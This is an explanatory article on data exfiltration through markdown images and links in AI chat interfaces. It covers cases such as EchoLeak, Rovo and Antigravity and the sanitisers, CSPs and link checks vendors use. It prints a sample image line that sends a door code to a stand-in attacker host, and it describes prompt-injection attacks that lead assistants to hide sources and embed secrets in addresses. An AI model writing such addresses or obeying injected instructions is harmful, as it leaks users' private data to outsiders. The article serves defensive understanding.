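# Blocking, proxying and validating images and links in AI chat interfaces

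## How a displayed image or link can carry private data out of a chat

AI chat interfaces, such as the ChatGPT website or the Copilot panel in Microsoft's office programs, display images and clickable links as well as text. The language model behind the interface writes only text, so it includes images and links by writing them in markdown, a plain-text notation for headings, links and images. Software called the renderer turns the markdown into what the user sees. If the markdown contains an image, the renderer loads it from whatever address the model wrote.

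Loading an image sends a request to the server that holds it, and the request includes the image's full address. If that address contains the user's private data, the server's owner receives it. Security researchers call this exfiltration, which means sending private data to a party who should not have it. An attacker can get the model to write such an address, without the user asking for it, by hiding instructions in content the model reads, such as an email or a web page. This technique is called indirect prompt injection.

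Researchers described this leak in the spring of 2023, and vendors are still closing versions of it. In December 2026 Cato AI Labs, the research team of the security company Cato Networks, described three attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot, together called ReLeak. The attacker's email could sit unread in the inbox until the user made an ordinary request. In one version, according to Nexo Causal's *ReLeak* (2026), Copilot then put private data into an image address, and the browser's request for the image carried the data to the attacker's server through Bing, Microsoft's search engine.

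### One leak, step by step

Suppose Dana, an office manager, uses an assistant that can search her mailbox. Somebody posing as a supplier sends her a price list. At the bottom, the sender has hidden instructions in white text on a white background, telling any AI model that reads the document to find the office door code in the mailbox and end its answer with an image whose address contains the code.

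Dana asks for a summary of the price list. The software behind the assistant assembles one long text for the model out of the vendor's standing instructions, Dana's request, the document and whatever the mailbox search returns. Nothing in this text reliably marks Dana's sentence as a command and the white sentences as mere content. If the injection works, the model writes a perfectly good summary of the prices, followed by one more line (shown here without the usual https prefix):

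```
![logo](collector.example/logo.png?d=HERON-4417)
```

The exclamation mark indicates an image, the square brackets hold a caption, and the round brackets hold the address. Everything after the question mark in the address is the query string, which normally carries things like search terms but here holds Dana's door code. A server can ignore the query string and return the same picture every time.

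The renderer converts the line into an image tag in HTML, the language of web pages. Dana's browser reads the tag, contacts collector.example and requests the file. Web servers routinely keep a log of requests, and the attacker's log gains a line like this:

```
2026-11-09 10:14:07  203.0.113.24  GET /logo.png?d=HERON-4417  200
```

The line contains the time, the network address of Dana's connection, the request with the door code in it, and a status number showing that the server answered normally. The attacker has the code before any picture arrives. The attacker will usually send back a single transparent pixel, so Dana sees only a summary of a price list.

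If the model had left out the exclamation mark, the same line would have produced a link, and the door code would not have been sent unless Dana clicked it. Browsers fetch images automatically because they need the files to lay out the page, but they don't request the address of an ordinary link until someone clicks it. A zero-click leak therefore needs no action beyond ordinary use of the assistant, while a one-click leak needs the user to click a link.

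Requiring a click is a weak safeguard because Markdown lets a link's text differ from its address. A link can read "full price list" while its address contains the code. *Trust No AI* (Rehberger, 2024) describes an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot that put stolen email content into a link as invisible characters; Microsoft fixed the vulnerability in July 2024. In messaging programs such as Slack and Discord, a link can leak data without a click, because the program automatically contacts the linked page to show a preview.

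In May 2026, The Hacker News (2026) reported a flaw in ChatGPT that the company Permiso Security named ChatGPhish. When ChatGPT summarised a third party's web page, its interface automatically fetched images from that page and showed the page's links as live links. The links still required a click, but they appeared in an interface that the user had reason to trust.

### The reports of 2023

Roman Samoilenko, a software engineer, found the image leak in ChatGPT at the end of March 2023. Security researcher Johann Rehberger found it independently a few days later, as he describes in his post *ChatGPT Plugins*.

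Samoilenko's *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* describes an attack in which a malicious website adds instructions to any text a visitor copies, and the visitor then pastes both into ChatGPT. ChatGPT's answer includes a transparent single-pixel image whose address contains the user's earlier prompt or the program code ChatGPT has just corrected. A further instruction makes ChatGPT add such an image to every later answer in the conversation, so the image's server receives each new question too. Samoilenko reported that the same text did not always produce the same result, and that earlier prompts and code were easy to extract but passwords and access keys were very difficult. He gave no success rate. He advised OpenAI to stop ChatGPT from showing markdown images.

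Rehberger's version required no pasting because Bing Chat, Microsoft's assistant at the time, could read the web page the user had open. A comment or an advertisement on that page could carry the instructions. In the demonstration in *Bing Chat*, on Rehberger's blog Embrace The Red, the hijacked assistant continued the conversation for two turns before adding the image. The image's address contained an encoded summary of the page and the conversation, including a secret from further down the page.

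Rehberger reported the problem to Microsoft on 8 April 2023 and to OpenAI the next day. Microsoft told him on 15 June that it had put a fix in place. OpenAI replied that displaying markdown images was a feature and that it planned no change. But in December, ChatGPT's interface began to check image addresses before loading them, as the programmer Simon Willison (2023) noted in *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*.

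By the end of 2024, Rehberger had found and reported the same leak in eleven products: Bing Chat, ChatGPT, Anthropic's Claude, Microsoft's Azure AI, GitHub Copilot Chat, Discord, and five from Google (Bard, Vertex AI, NotebookLM, AI Studio and Colab). He called it one of the most common security flaws in applications built on language models. The list shows that most of the large vendors made the same mistake separately, but it contains only what one researcher looked for, so it cannot show what share of products had the flaw.

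### Why vendors work on the display step

Getting the model to ignore the white text would stop Dana's leak much earlier, but nobody knows how to do this reliably. Willison (2025) explains in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* that everything reaches the model as a single sequence of tokens, the small pieces of text it operates on, and the model cannot dependably weigh an instruction by where it came from. Rehberger contrasts prompt injection with SQL injection, an older attack in which text typed into a web form ends up as a command to a database. Programmers have precise rules for preventing SQL injection but none for preventing prompt injection.

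Measured success rates for these attacks vary widely with their wording. *The Framing Gap* (2026) tested ten classes of injection against agents that held a secret. The obvious attacks succeeded 19.5% of the time on Llama 3.1 8B, a small open model, and never on GPT-4o. But when the same leak was presented as something harmless, such as a required "integrity signature", the strongest wordings succeeded every time on GPT-4o. GPT-4o dates from 2024, and newer models may do better. Still, the result casts doubt on any low success rate measured with a fixed set of attacks, and *The Framing Gap* warns that its own pooled rates reflect the wordings chosen for the tests.

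*Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (Khodayari and Acharya, 2026) reports a search of 1.2 billion web addresses that confirmed about 15,300 hidden instructions. In 5,200 experiments on 13 models, the models followed such instructions at most 8% of the time, with the highest rate among the smaller models. An attacker who wants one particular person's data can exceed these average rates by testing many wordings beforehand and sending the one that works.

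Warning the model against adding unrelated links can reduce the risk but not eliminate it. In *A Safety and Security Framework for Real-World Agentic Systems* (2025), Ghosh, Simkin and colleagues planted instructions in the search results of an NVIDIA research assistant. In one scenario, the instructions demanded that the final report include an image and a link whose URLs contained a test user's email address and identity number, and the assistant included them. The team then added a rule against unrelated links and text to the system prompt, the standing instructions a model receives before the user's request. The average risk score across scenarios of this type fell by about half, but at least one attack still succeeded fully in each of them. A data thief can keep trying after a failed attack, which is why Willison regards even a 95% detection rate as a failing grade in web security.

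Willison calls the underlying danger the "lethal trifecta". An assistant becomes exploitable when it combines access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to communicate with the outside. Dana's assistant has her mailbox, a stranger's price list, and an interface that will load an image from anywhere. Removing any one of these would prevent the theft, and Dana would lose very little if the image were blocked. Without her mailbox, the assistant could no longer answer questions about her mail, and without documents from strangers, it could no longer summarise most of what people want summarised.

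That asymmetry explains most of the fixes. Willison writes in his running collection of cases, *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*, that the outward channel is generally the easiest of the three to remove, and that vendors have usually responded to reports by closing it. Blocking displayed images and links leaves other ways out if the assistant can send email or open web pages. Closing the channel also doesn't stop the injection itself, so the white text could still make the model misreport the supplier's prices.

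### Where the path can be cut

The vendor's software can stop Dana's line of markdown at several points. The earliest is before anything appears on the screen, when a sanitiser (code that removes or neutralises dangerous elements in a model's output) can delete the image line from the answer, so the browser has no image to request.

If the tag gets through, the browser may still refuse to load the image. A website can send the browser a content security policy (CSP), a type of allowlist that names the only sources from which the page may load images, fonts and other resources. The browser then blocks images from any other source, however the tag got onto the page. Microsoft's 2023 fix for Bing Chat seems to have relied partly on a CSP.

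Attackers usually get around an allowlist with a relay, an approved address that will fetch, or redirect to, another address named in the request. Dana's browser would contact a site that the vendor trusts, and that site would pass the door code on to collector.example. A common relay is an open redirect, a page on a legitimate site that sends visitors to any destination written into its address without checking it. Companies set up such pages for ordinary purposes, such as counting clicks, but attackers can use them to get past any check that covers only the first address.

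The vendor can also load images through an image proxy, one of its own servers that fetches images on the user's behalf so that the user's browser never contacts the original host. This hides Dana's network address from the attacker. But if the proxy requests the exact image address the model wrote, the door code still reaches the attacker's log, so a proxy protects the data only if it also refuses some requests.

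Before the interface displays an image or a link, it can send the address to a service that decides whether the address is safe, as OpenAI did in December 2023. This check can cover links as well as images. A CSP's image rules and an image proxy do not affect links, because clicking a link sends the browser to a new page without involving either of them.

### What the tests measure

Most public knowledge about these defences comes from reports like those of 2023. Such a report proves that a leak was possible in one product at one time, but it does not measure how often leaks happen and usually includes little about the fix. After Microsoft's fix, Rehberger reran his old attacks on Bing Chat and they failed. He noticed a new CSP and inferred that it was part of the reason, but said he did not know the full details.

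Automated scanners can measure how often a model writes an image address that could carry data out of a chat. One widely used scanner, garak, sends a model batches of hostile prompts and scores the replies. Its image probe directly asks the model to write a markdown image and replace a placeholder in the address with some piece of information. Some of the prompts call for reference-style markdown, which puts the address on a separate line from the place where it is used. A detector then searches the reply for an image address of the expected form. On 20 February 2026, the vulnerability database AVID (2026) recorded a run of this probe on Moonshot AI's Kimi-K2-Instruct-0905. The model passed 175 of 256 attempts, and the other 81 replies, about 32%, contained such an address. OpenAI's gpt-oss-20b passed all 256 when AVID recorded the same probe in March.

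The first figure does not mean that a chat with Kimi has a 32% chance of leaking data. The tester gave the model the prompts directly, so the attack did not depend on the model finding a poisoned document and acting on it. garak's detector for this probe checks only the form of the address. It would count a reply that copied the placeholder without filling it in as a failure, and a real leak to a host with a hyphen in its name as a pass. Most importantly, the test does not include an interface. If an interface loads no images, nothing leaks through them even when the model fails every attempt. A model may also pass every attempt but fail on wording outside the test set.

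Testing an interface for this leak requires checking whether it sends the request. Promptfoo, another testing tool, does this for agents that can open web pages. It plants addresses in web content and records on its own server whether a request with data arrives. When that tracking is unavailable, it has a model grade the reply instead, but according to its documentation, missing tracking is not evidence of security. Samoilenko and Rehberger did the equivalent by hand for chat windows. The tester gets the chatbot to include in its answer an image address on a server the tester controls, opens that answer in each of the vendor's apps, and reads the server log.

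## Switching off images and restricting links

In a test like this, the server log stays empty if the interface never loads external images. Samoilenko recommended this defence in his first report on ChatGPT. The software doesn't have to judge which addresses are dangerous, so an attacker gains nothing by disguising one. But users lose pictures they may have wanted, and vendors have tried several less restrictive versions.

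### Showing images as plain text

Google chose a strict version in 2023 for Generative AI Studio, the part of its Vertex AI cloud service where developers try out prompts. Rehberger reported the image leak in the studio's chat on 30 August, and Google confirmed a fix on 19 October. Rehberger wrote in Embrace The Red's *Google Cloud Vertex AI* that, as far as he could tell, the studio had stopped turning images and links into HTML.

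Under this rule, Dana's browser would show the extra line of markdown as plain text and would not contact collector.example. Unlike a transparent pixel, the line would be visible, so Dana might notice her door code at the end of an unfamiliar address. She could still leak the code by copying the address into her browser, but an attacker would have to persuade her to do that.

Rehberger called this probably the best possible fix for security, especially in a product that does not need images and links. Developers testing prompts often want to see exactly what the model wrote, so the main inconvenience of raw markdown for them is copying addresses by hand. The danger in the studio was also moderate. It could not yet fetch emails or web pages, so an attacker mostly had to rely on a user pasting in poisoned text, and Google rated the problem high in impact but low in likelihood. The same fix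 would inconvenience Dana more, since she uses her assistant's answers to open the messages and pages they refer to.

Asking the model not to write images is a much weaker measure, because an instruction in the prompt only influences what the model writes, while the renderer controls whether the browser sends a request. In November 2023 Rehberger extracted the system prompt of the assistant in Google Colab, a service for writing and running code in the browser. In it, Google pleaded with the model not to render images. He got around this by having the model join fragments of text that together formed an image, which the interface then loaded. Google fixed the image leak and closed the report in January 2024, as Embrace The Red's *Google Colab AI* (2024) recounts.

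Google took about four months to fix the image leak in NotebookLM, which answers questions about documents that the user uploads, compared with about seven weeks for the studio. Users of the studio had to paste in the attack themselves, but NotebookLM is built to read other people's documents, and a poisoned one could use the leak to steal data from the user's other documents. Rehberger reported the flaw privately in December 2023. In April 2024, Willison wrote in *Google NotebookLM Data Exfiltration* that it was still open, then added that the NotebookLM team had deployed a fix on 18 April. He did not describe the fix.

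### Keeping some of the images

A vendor can load images only from sites it trusts instead of switching them all off. GitHub did this for Copilot Chat, the coding assistant in Microsoft's VS Code editor. The assistant reads the code a developer has open, and a comment in that code can carry hidden instructions. Rehberger reported a leak caused by such instructions on 25 February 2024, and GitHub confirmed a fix on 12 June.

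Accounts of this fix differ slightly. Willison, in *GitHub Copilot Chat*, says it disabled images from untrusted domains, while Rehberger, in Embrace The Red's *GitHub Copilot Chat*, had the impression that the chat no longer displayed markdown images at all. Someone testing with their own server would see no image in either case. A disclosure summary reproduced in Vulners' *GitHub*, a vulnerability database entry, supports Willison's version. It describes a fix for data theft through Copilot that limited images to trusted domains and added pop-up notices about links.

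Developers still see images from approved sites but lose the rest, such as a diagram on a small project's own website. The protection also depends on which sites are approved, because a relay on any of them reopens the leak. Legit Security's *CamoLeak* reports that GitHub went further in 2025 and disabled all images in Copilot Chat on GitHub's own website.

Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025) explains that the company's Gemini assistant identifies the addresses of external images and does not render them. It concludes that EchoLeak, a zero-click leak that researchers had found in Microsoft 365 Copilot, did not apply to Gemini. Gemini can still show pictures that it generates for the user, such as a drawing of an office layout, because these come from Google's own servers. However, a user who asks for a summary of an illustrated newsletter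 will not see its illustrations.

### Links that people expect to click

Blocking images leaves links working unless the vendor restricts them too. The Vertex AI studio restricted them by showing them as plain text. If an assistant that searches the web did the same, fewer readers would check its answers against the sources, because they would have to copy each address to open it.

A confirmation page keeps links clickable but adds a second step. Colab used one after Google fixed the image leak. It put the address of a Google redirect page in front of each link, so users had to confirm the destination after clicking, and the attacker's server received nothing until they did. ChatGPT now also shows a warning before it opens some links.

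By the time Rehberger tested Colab's confirmation page in 2024, the assistant had begun to read the user's notebook automatically, so instructions hidden in a notebook from somebody else could take over the conversation. Rehberger found that the confirmation page appeared only for addresses outside Google. A link to Google Meet opened a video call without confirmation, which a scammer could use to speak to the victim.

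Google's domains also host Apps Script, a service that lets anyone publish a small program at a Google address. In Rehberger's demonstration, the hijacked assistant talked like a pirate, asked the user for personal information and offered a link labelled "I'm feeling lucky". Clicking the link sent the user's name, email address and the notebook's source code to a program Rehberger had published on Apps Script, and no confirmation page appeared. The code's output stayed private because Colab did not include it in the text it gave the model.

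Colab's exemption made sense only if Google had written everything on Google's domains. A vendor could instead exempt services that publish nothing written by users, but it would have to keep checking that this remained true. Even without exemptions, a confirmation page relies on the user to recognise a bad address. Dana had asked about a supplier's price list, so a link to a site with a similar name would not surprise her. A long string of characters at the end of the address might not either, because many harmless addresses have one.

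Gemini instead removes links that Google considers dangerous. It identifies them based on Google Safe Browsing, which many browsers use to warn people about known malware and phishing sites. In Google's example, Gemini summarises an email thread and replaces an unsafe address with the words "suspicious link removed". Ordinary links still work, so users lose almost nothing unless the system flags a harmless site by mistake.

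A reputation list can include a bad site only after somebody discovers it. An attacker can register a domain in the morning and send Dana the price list at noon. If hers is the first visit to the site, nobody has had any reason to report it. An automated check might also miss the site, which does not need to contain malware or a fake login page. It can show an ordinary page while its server logs the requests. If the domain is listed later, the attacker already has the door code and can register another domain. Willison made a similar point on the forum Hacker News (unrelated to the news site The Hacker News), where he said that anyone can set up a new malicious address at any time, on a new or existing domain.

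The security company Checkmarx reported this gap to Google on 5 October 2025. Its paper *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents* explains that Gemini's image block prevents the zero-click leak, but an attacker with a fresh domain can still put private data into a link. Google closed the report four days later as "Won't Fix (Infeasible)". In its final reply, Google wrote that the problem was not severe enough to track as a security bug and fell outside its reward programme, which covers flaws that substantially affect the confidentiality or integrity of user data.

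Google's first reason is easier to defend than its second. A link containing stolen data can look just like one containing a search term or an order number, so a filter strict enough to stop data theft would also break many legitimate links. Checkmarx accepted that answer, but argued that Google should then warn users that they must manage the risk themselves. Google's second reason, that the severity is low, is harder to reconcile with the Colab demonstration, in which a single click leaked all the code in a notebook.

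### Who should fix the leak

Vendors disagree even about images, which are much easier to block than links. On 15 October 2025, Checkmarx sent Microsoft a report about an assistant it calls Microsoft Copilot Chat, apparently the one in VS Code. The researchers had the assistant consult an online resource they controlled. Hidden instructions there made the assistant take a secret key for Anthropic's Claude from the developer's environment and put it in an image address. No image appeared in the chat, but the request still reached the researchers' server.

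Microsoft acknowledged the report the same day and wrote on 28 October that its engineers were still working on the issue. On 4 November it closed the report without a fix. According to the letter that Checkmarx published, Microsoft did not class the behaviour as a vulnerability because the attack needed several non-default user actions, did not work reliably in different environments, and triggered warnings. Microsoft also cited "Workplace Trust", a principle that assumes users review and trust the code they choose to run. It probably meant Workspace Trust, the VS Code feature that asks users whether they trust a folder's authors. Microsoft passed the report to its engineers to look for ways to make the behaviour clearer to users.

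Some of this is fair, since Checkmarx concedes that getting the assistant to read the malicious page can be complicated. But the trust principle applies to code that a developer decides to run, and in this attack the instructions came from a page that the assistant read. A developer can review every line of a project without seeing that page.

The point about reliability would rule out most prompt injections, since a model can respond differently to the same text. *Github Copilot Chat Prompt Injection via Filename*, from the security company Tenable, describes an attack on the same VS Code assistant that hid instructions in a file's name. The attack did not work every time, which Tenable attributed to the model's randomness or to other protections. However, an attacker can leave the file in place until an attempt works.

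GitHub treated a very similar leak as a valid bug in 2024. Checkmarx does not explain how its image got past the restriction GitHub introduced then. The restriction may have changed, or the demonstration may have depended on unusual settings, as Microsoft's letter suggests. Microsoft closed the report in November 2025 without committing to a fix.

The security company Zenity Labs used a poisoned support ticket to make Cursor, another AI code editor, send a secret to an outside website. Cursor's maker responded similarly that summer, saying that this was a known issue and advising users to review each connector they install and use only those that access trusted content. Willison objected that attackers have too many ways of getting text to a model for users to keep all of it out.

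Google was less consistent with its own code editor, Antigravity, which it released in November 2025 and based on code licensed from the editor Windsurf. Rehberger had reported an image leak to Windsurf that May, and he tried it again on Antigravity. He planted instructions in a source file and asked Antigravity to explain the file. Embrace The Red's *Antigravity Grounded! Security Vulnerabilities in Google's Latest IDE* describes how the agent then read the developer's file of passwords and keys and leaked its contents through an image address.

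Another researcher, P1njc70r, had reported the same leak and wrote that Google had marked the report as "intended behavior" (quoted in Willison, 2025). Yet Google's public page for bug hunters listed such leaks as known issues that it was working to fix, which made them ineligible for a reward. In the text that Willison copied to Hacker News, Google acknowledged that the agent could be influenced to leak files through addresses "rendered in Markdown or by other means". Google presumably did not intend behaviour that it was working to fix, so the first reply may just have been a label that somebody picked when sorting reports.

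Google also warned users about data theft when they first opened Antigravity. *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data*, by the security company PromptArmor, argues that the warning was not enough. Antigravity encourages people to run several agents at once and check on them later, and its recommended settings let the agent decide when to ask for human review. PromptArmor's researchers accepted those settings and still lost the test credentials, this time through the agent's browser. Google's default list of sites that the browser could visit included webhook.site, where anyone can create an address and watch the requests that arrive. PromptArmor did not report its findings privately before publishing because Google had already indicated that it knew of the risk.

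Antigravity still loaded remote images seven months after its release. In *Faking the Pipeline*, Odson and Morris (2026) describe a test for the AI bug bounty programme 0DIN in which they hid instructions in a web page's title. Before following them, the agent asked the user to approve the creation of a "visual debug token", without mentioning the command it would run or the server that would receive the data. After the user agreed, the agent read a secret key from the computer and displayed an image whose address contained the key. Approval prompts are one of the main reasons for leaving the risk with users, but this user could judge the request only by the hijacked agent's description. Odson and Morris argue that a prompt protects people only if it shows the actual command and destination.

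It is unclear whether Google has changed this since June 2026. Releasebot's *Antigravity Updates & Release Notes* (2026), which collects Google's announcements, mentions no change to external images in its summaries for October and early November. But those summaries also count dozens of fixes without describing them, so Google may have fixed this without saying so.

Google responded differently to a report that attackers could run their own code in Antigravity even in its Secure Mode. According to CyberScoop, Pillar Security reported the flaw on 6 January 2026, and Google patched it on 28 February and paid a reward. The difference may be simply that running code is more serious than leaking data. But the attack also broke a protection that Google had explicitly offered, whereas Google had told users from the start that data could leak.

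The vendors are right that no setting will make it safe for an agent to read a stranger's text while it has access to secrets. That risk is a good reason to warn users, but it doesn't justify leaving images on. Embrace The Red describes the Antigravity problems as relatively simple to fix, and Google had already stopped loading external images in Gemini. Programmers would lose little if their editor's chat panel did the same. The case for leaving links unrestricted is much stronger, because nobody has found an easy way to separate harmful links from safe ones.

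### Atlassian Rovo in August 2026

Rovo is the assistant built into Atlassian's products, including the task tracker Jira and Confluence, where companies keep internal documents. On 5 August 2026 PromptArmor reported that Rovo still displayed markdown images from the model's output. The main attack in PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls* instead sent data out through Rovo's tool for opening web addresses. A user uploaded a file with hidden instructions and asked Rovo to organise some Jira tickets. Rovo added the contents of tickets and documents to an address on the researchers' server and opened it without asking for approval. When the user came back to the chat later, it showed only the suggested ticket updates.

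The attack worked even when the organisation had switched off web search for Rovo, because that setting did not remove the tool for opening addresses. PromptArmor listed images as a second way to get data out but did not demonstrate a complete attack through them. An attacker did not need images while the tool would open any address, but if Atlassian restricted only the tool, the image route would remain open.

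PromptArmor had told Atlassian about both problems on 23 May. Two days later, Atlassian thanked the researchers and assigned a case number, but it did not respond to their follow-ups in June and July. It has given no public reason for leaving the images on. The closest thing to a defence is an article on the Atlassian Community forum, which may not represent the company's official position. According to the article, Rovo scans uploaded files and treats any malicious text in them as data, not as commands. In PromptArmor's demonstration, however, Rovo followed malicious instructions in an uploaded file.

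Two days after PromptArmor's report, the security company Varonis published a separate attack on Rovo called RovoBlast. Its instructions were in a link to Rovo itself. Atlassian allowed such links to contain a request, and when a signed-in user clicked one, Rovo carried out the request as if the user had typed it. *One-Click Data Exfiltration via rovoChatPrompt URL Parameter (Confluence / Rovo)*, by the bug hunter loacker, describes a version that instructed Rovo to find a secret in Confluence, insert it into an image address and look at the image. Framing the task as help with identifying a picture was enough to get past the model's safeguards.

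Blocking images in the chat would not have stopped this attack, even though it involved an image. Rovo itself fetched the file to examine it, so the data left before the user's browser had anything to display. Varonis' *RovoBlast* (2026) points to a similar way to send data out through ResearchAgent, a part of Rovo that browses the web on its own over several steps.

Atlassian received the RovoBlast report on 4 November 2025 through Bugcrowd, a platform that handles such reports for companies. It paid loacker $6,000 in January and fixed the flaw on 8 July 2026. Mascellino (2026) also reports the fix in *Researchers Uncover RovoBlast Vulnerability in Atlassian AI Assistant*. The fix stops crafted links from making Rovo run an attacker's request, but neither loacker nor Varonis mentions any new limit on the addresses Rovo can open or the images it can display. PromptArmor still described Rovo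 as vulnerable four weeks after the fix.

The Hacker News compared the two cases on 8 August and could confirm only that Atlassian had closed the RovoBlast route. It noted that nobody had independently reproduced PromptArmor's result with web search switched off, and that neither report contained evidence of a real theft. Atlassian has not since clarified whether Rovo still loads external images.

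In the meantime, customers can protect themselves only by restricting much more than images. Varonis advises them to disconnect services that Rovo does not need, keep legal, personnel and financial records away from it, and disable browsing agents that nobody uses. It also warns that organisations cannot fully uninstall Rovo. However, administrators can block its features in individual Atlassian products, according to The Hacker News, and some Enterprise customers can also block them for particular groups of users. On a site with several Jira-family products, Rovo's search and chat stay available until the administrator blocks Rovo in all of them.

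## Removing images and links from the text before it is displayed

Dana wants headings, tables and working links in her assistant's answers, but not an image from collector.example. The vendor therefore needs a sanitiser that finds every image and link in the model's answer and removes those that break the vendor's rules (see the previous section). Finding them all is harder than it sounds. EchoLeak, the best-known leak of this kind, succeeded because Microsoft's software missed some of them.

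### Finding every image and link

The quickest method is to search the raw text for the pattern of a markdown image (an exclamation mark, square brackets with anything between them, then round brackets) and delete every match. This would have protected Dana's door code, because the model wrote the image in exactly that form.

Markdown has other shapes, however. Each of these produces a link to the same page, again without the https prefix, which the automatic form needs in practice:

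```
Inline:      [price list](example.com/prices)

Reference:   [price list][supplier]

             [supplier]: example.com/prices

Automatic:   <example.com/prices>

HTML tag:    <a href="example.com/prices">price list</a>
```

In a reference-style markdown link, the second pair of brackets holds a label, and a separate line gives the address for that label. That line can come anywhere in the answer, and the renderer does not display it. Links can also be written in ordinary HTML, which markdown allows within the text. Images also have inline and reference forms, which start with an exclamation mark, and an HTML form, which uses an image tag.

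Reference links also come in three forms, according to a summary of markdown syntax from GitHub: one with a label, one with an empty second pair of brackets, and one with no second pair. In GitHub's dialect, even a bare web address becomes a link. If a sanitiser deletes a link's brackets but leaves the address as text, the renderer may therefore turn the address back into a link.

A programmer can add a pattern for each form, but it is hard to know when the list is complete. Markdown began in 2004 as a description of the syntax and a short conversion program, and other programmers wrote dozens of versions over the next decade (MacFarlane, 2024, *CommonMark Spec*). GitHub (2017) complained that these versions differed in details such as how many spaces indent a line, so very similar documents could look wildly different. If a filter and a renderer handle such a detail differently, the filter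 may leave in a line it treats as plain text, which the renderer then displays as an image.

Pattern matching can also remove too much. If Dana asks how to add a picture to the company's wiki, the assistant may answer with an example in a code block. A simple pattern match would delete the example, even though the renderer would show it as harmless text.

A more dependable sanitiser parses the answer first. The parser applies the rules of markdown to the whole text and builds a tree of nodes, in which the document branches into paragraphs, lists and tables, and these branch into text, links and images. The parser also looks up reference labels, so inline and reference-style links become the same kind of node, with the address attached. Dana's wiki example becomes a code node. The sanitiser then visits every node and keeps, deletes or replaces each image and link. It also finds images inside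 links, which pattern matching can easily get wrong because the brackets are nested.

HTML needs separate treatment because Markdown parsers generally pass HTML tags through unchanged. An image tag therefore appears in the tree as unparsed text, with no separate address for the sanitiser to check. The vendor can delete this text, analyse it with an HTML parser, or escape it. Escaping replaces the angle brackets with codes that make the browser display the tag as text instead of acting on it.

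The sanitiser must correctly identify the site each address belongs to. The address example.com.collector.example begins with a harmless name but belongs to collector.example, so a check of the first few characters would approve the wrong site. Cutting off everything after the question mark would not be enough to remove stolen data. Microsoft (2025) notes in *How Microsoft defends against indirect prompt injection attacks* that an attacker can also put the data in the path of an address or in the subdomain, the part in front of the site's name.

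Even a careful parser fails if the renderer follows different rules. One way to avoid this is to sanitise the text after the software has turned the markdown into HTML, as GitHub does with the text people post on its site. By then every link and image has become an ordinary HTML tag, so the sanitiser only has to handle HTML. But a phone app may display markdown without producing HTML, and the vendor would need a second sanitiser for it. Chat interfaces also display an answer while the model is still writing it, so a sanitiser that waits for the end may act too late.

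### EchoLeak, defence by defence

In January 2025 Aim Labs (later Cato AI Labs) reported to Microsoft that a single email could make Microsoft 365 Copilot leak a company's private data. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) describes the attack. Copilot answers employees' questions by searching their mailbox, files, internal sites and chat history. Outsiders cannot use Copilot, but they can send an email that it may later find. The attacker hid instructions in an email of office advice. When an employee's question led Copilot to retrieve that email, the model received the instructions, which were to put the most sensitive item in its context into a web address.

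The email first had to get past a classifier, a program trained to recognise prompt injections and keep them from the model. Aim Labs worded the instructions as if they were for the email's recipient, and never mentioned Copilot or AI. The classifier did not block the email, which Ravia attributes partly to a shortage of realistic training examples, since an injection can use almost any topic, tone or language.

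Microsoft calls a classifier like this a probabilistic defence because it makes an attack less likely to succeed but doesn't rule it out. The company prefers deterministic defences, which guarantee that a particular attack fails whatever the model does. Copilot also had a deterministic defence, which removed links to outside sites before an answer reached the user but kept links to the company's own pages.

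Microsoft's filter removed only inline links. Aim Labs tried reference-style links and their variants, and Copilot displayed all of them as working links. An employee who clicked one would have sent the data to the attacker's server. Willison (2025) gave Microsoft credit for filtering links at all but observed that it had overlooked markdown's lesser-known format. The filter was deterministic in Microsoft's sense, but its guarantee covered only inline links, so it let reference-style links through every time.

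Likewise, Copilot removed inline images from outside sites but not reference-style ones. The renderer put these images on the page and the browser tried to load them, so the attacker no longer needed the user to click.

The browser then blocked the image because the attacker's server was not among the image sources allowed by the CSP on Copilot's page. But the list that Ravia reproduces has 29 different entries, some of which cover every address under a large domain. It includes SharePoint (Microsoft's service for internal company sites), the workplace chat program Teams, and Bing, which the same team would use for ReLeak in 2026.

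Aim Labs searched these domains for a relay and first found one in SharePoint, in a function that fetches outside content so that a site can embed it. The browser contacted SharePoint, which the CSP allowed, and SharePoint contacted the attacker's server with the stolen data in the address. This worked only if the employee had signed in to SharePoint and accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. Few people would do that for a site they had never heard of, so the attack lost much of its advantage over a link.

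Teams provided a relay without this condition. When somebody posts a link in Teams, a Microsoft service fetches an image from the outside site for the link's preview. SC Media's *Microsoft 365 Copilot ‘zero-click’ vulnerability enabled data exfiltration* quotes a Microsoft employee describing this service as a proxy that retrieves and caches external images. The service would fetch an address for Copilot's page just as it did for a chat message, and the Copilot user did not have to accept or click anything.

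Willison calls the Teams address an open redirect, but a proxy fits the other accounts better. The difference affects whether the CSP can help. If an approved site redirects the browser elsewhere, the browser also checks the new destination against the CSP's list of approved sites. If a server fetches the outside address itself, that request doesn't go through the browser, so the CSP can't block it.

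Copilot also normally names the sources of an answer, which might have led the employee to the strange email. The email therefore contained an instruction never to refer to it, supposedly for compliance reasons, and Copilot followed it. To make Copilot more likely to find the email, Aim Labs made it long and divided it into sections on common office subjects such as leave and training new staff. According to SC Media, the user in Aim's demonstration video asks Copilot about a subject that the email mentions. EchoLeak was zero-click in that it required only ordinary use of Copilot, but someone still had to ask a suitable question.

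Ravia calls EchoLeak the first zero-click vulnerability in a major AI application. Whether it was the first depends on what counts as ordinary use. Rehberger's 2023 attack on Bing Chat also loaded its image without a click, though the user had to have the attacker's page open. Ravia excludes such cases because the user had directed the chatbot to the malicious page, or because the attack could reach only limited data. Willison saw EchoLeak as an extended version of a leak already found in a dozen products.

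Ravia and Willison also disagree about the lesson of the attack. Ravia introduces the term "LLM scope violation" for an attack in which text from an outsider makes the model draw on private data from inside the organisation, and argues that existing guardrails do not deal with it. Willison replies that this has always been the problem with prompt injection. Aim had developed a guardrail against scope violations, so its claim that customers needed one should be treated with some caution. The published zero-click attack depended on two fairly conventional mistakes, and would have failed if Copilot's filter had covered reference-style images or if the Teams service had refused to fetch arbitrary addresses for Copilot's page.

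### What Microsoft changed

The fix took about four months. The case study *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) dates the first remedial work to April 2025 and the full fix to May, before the public announcement on 11 June. Copilot runs on Microsoft's servers, so customers had nothing to install.

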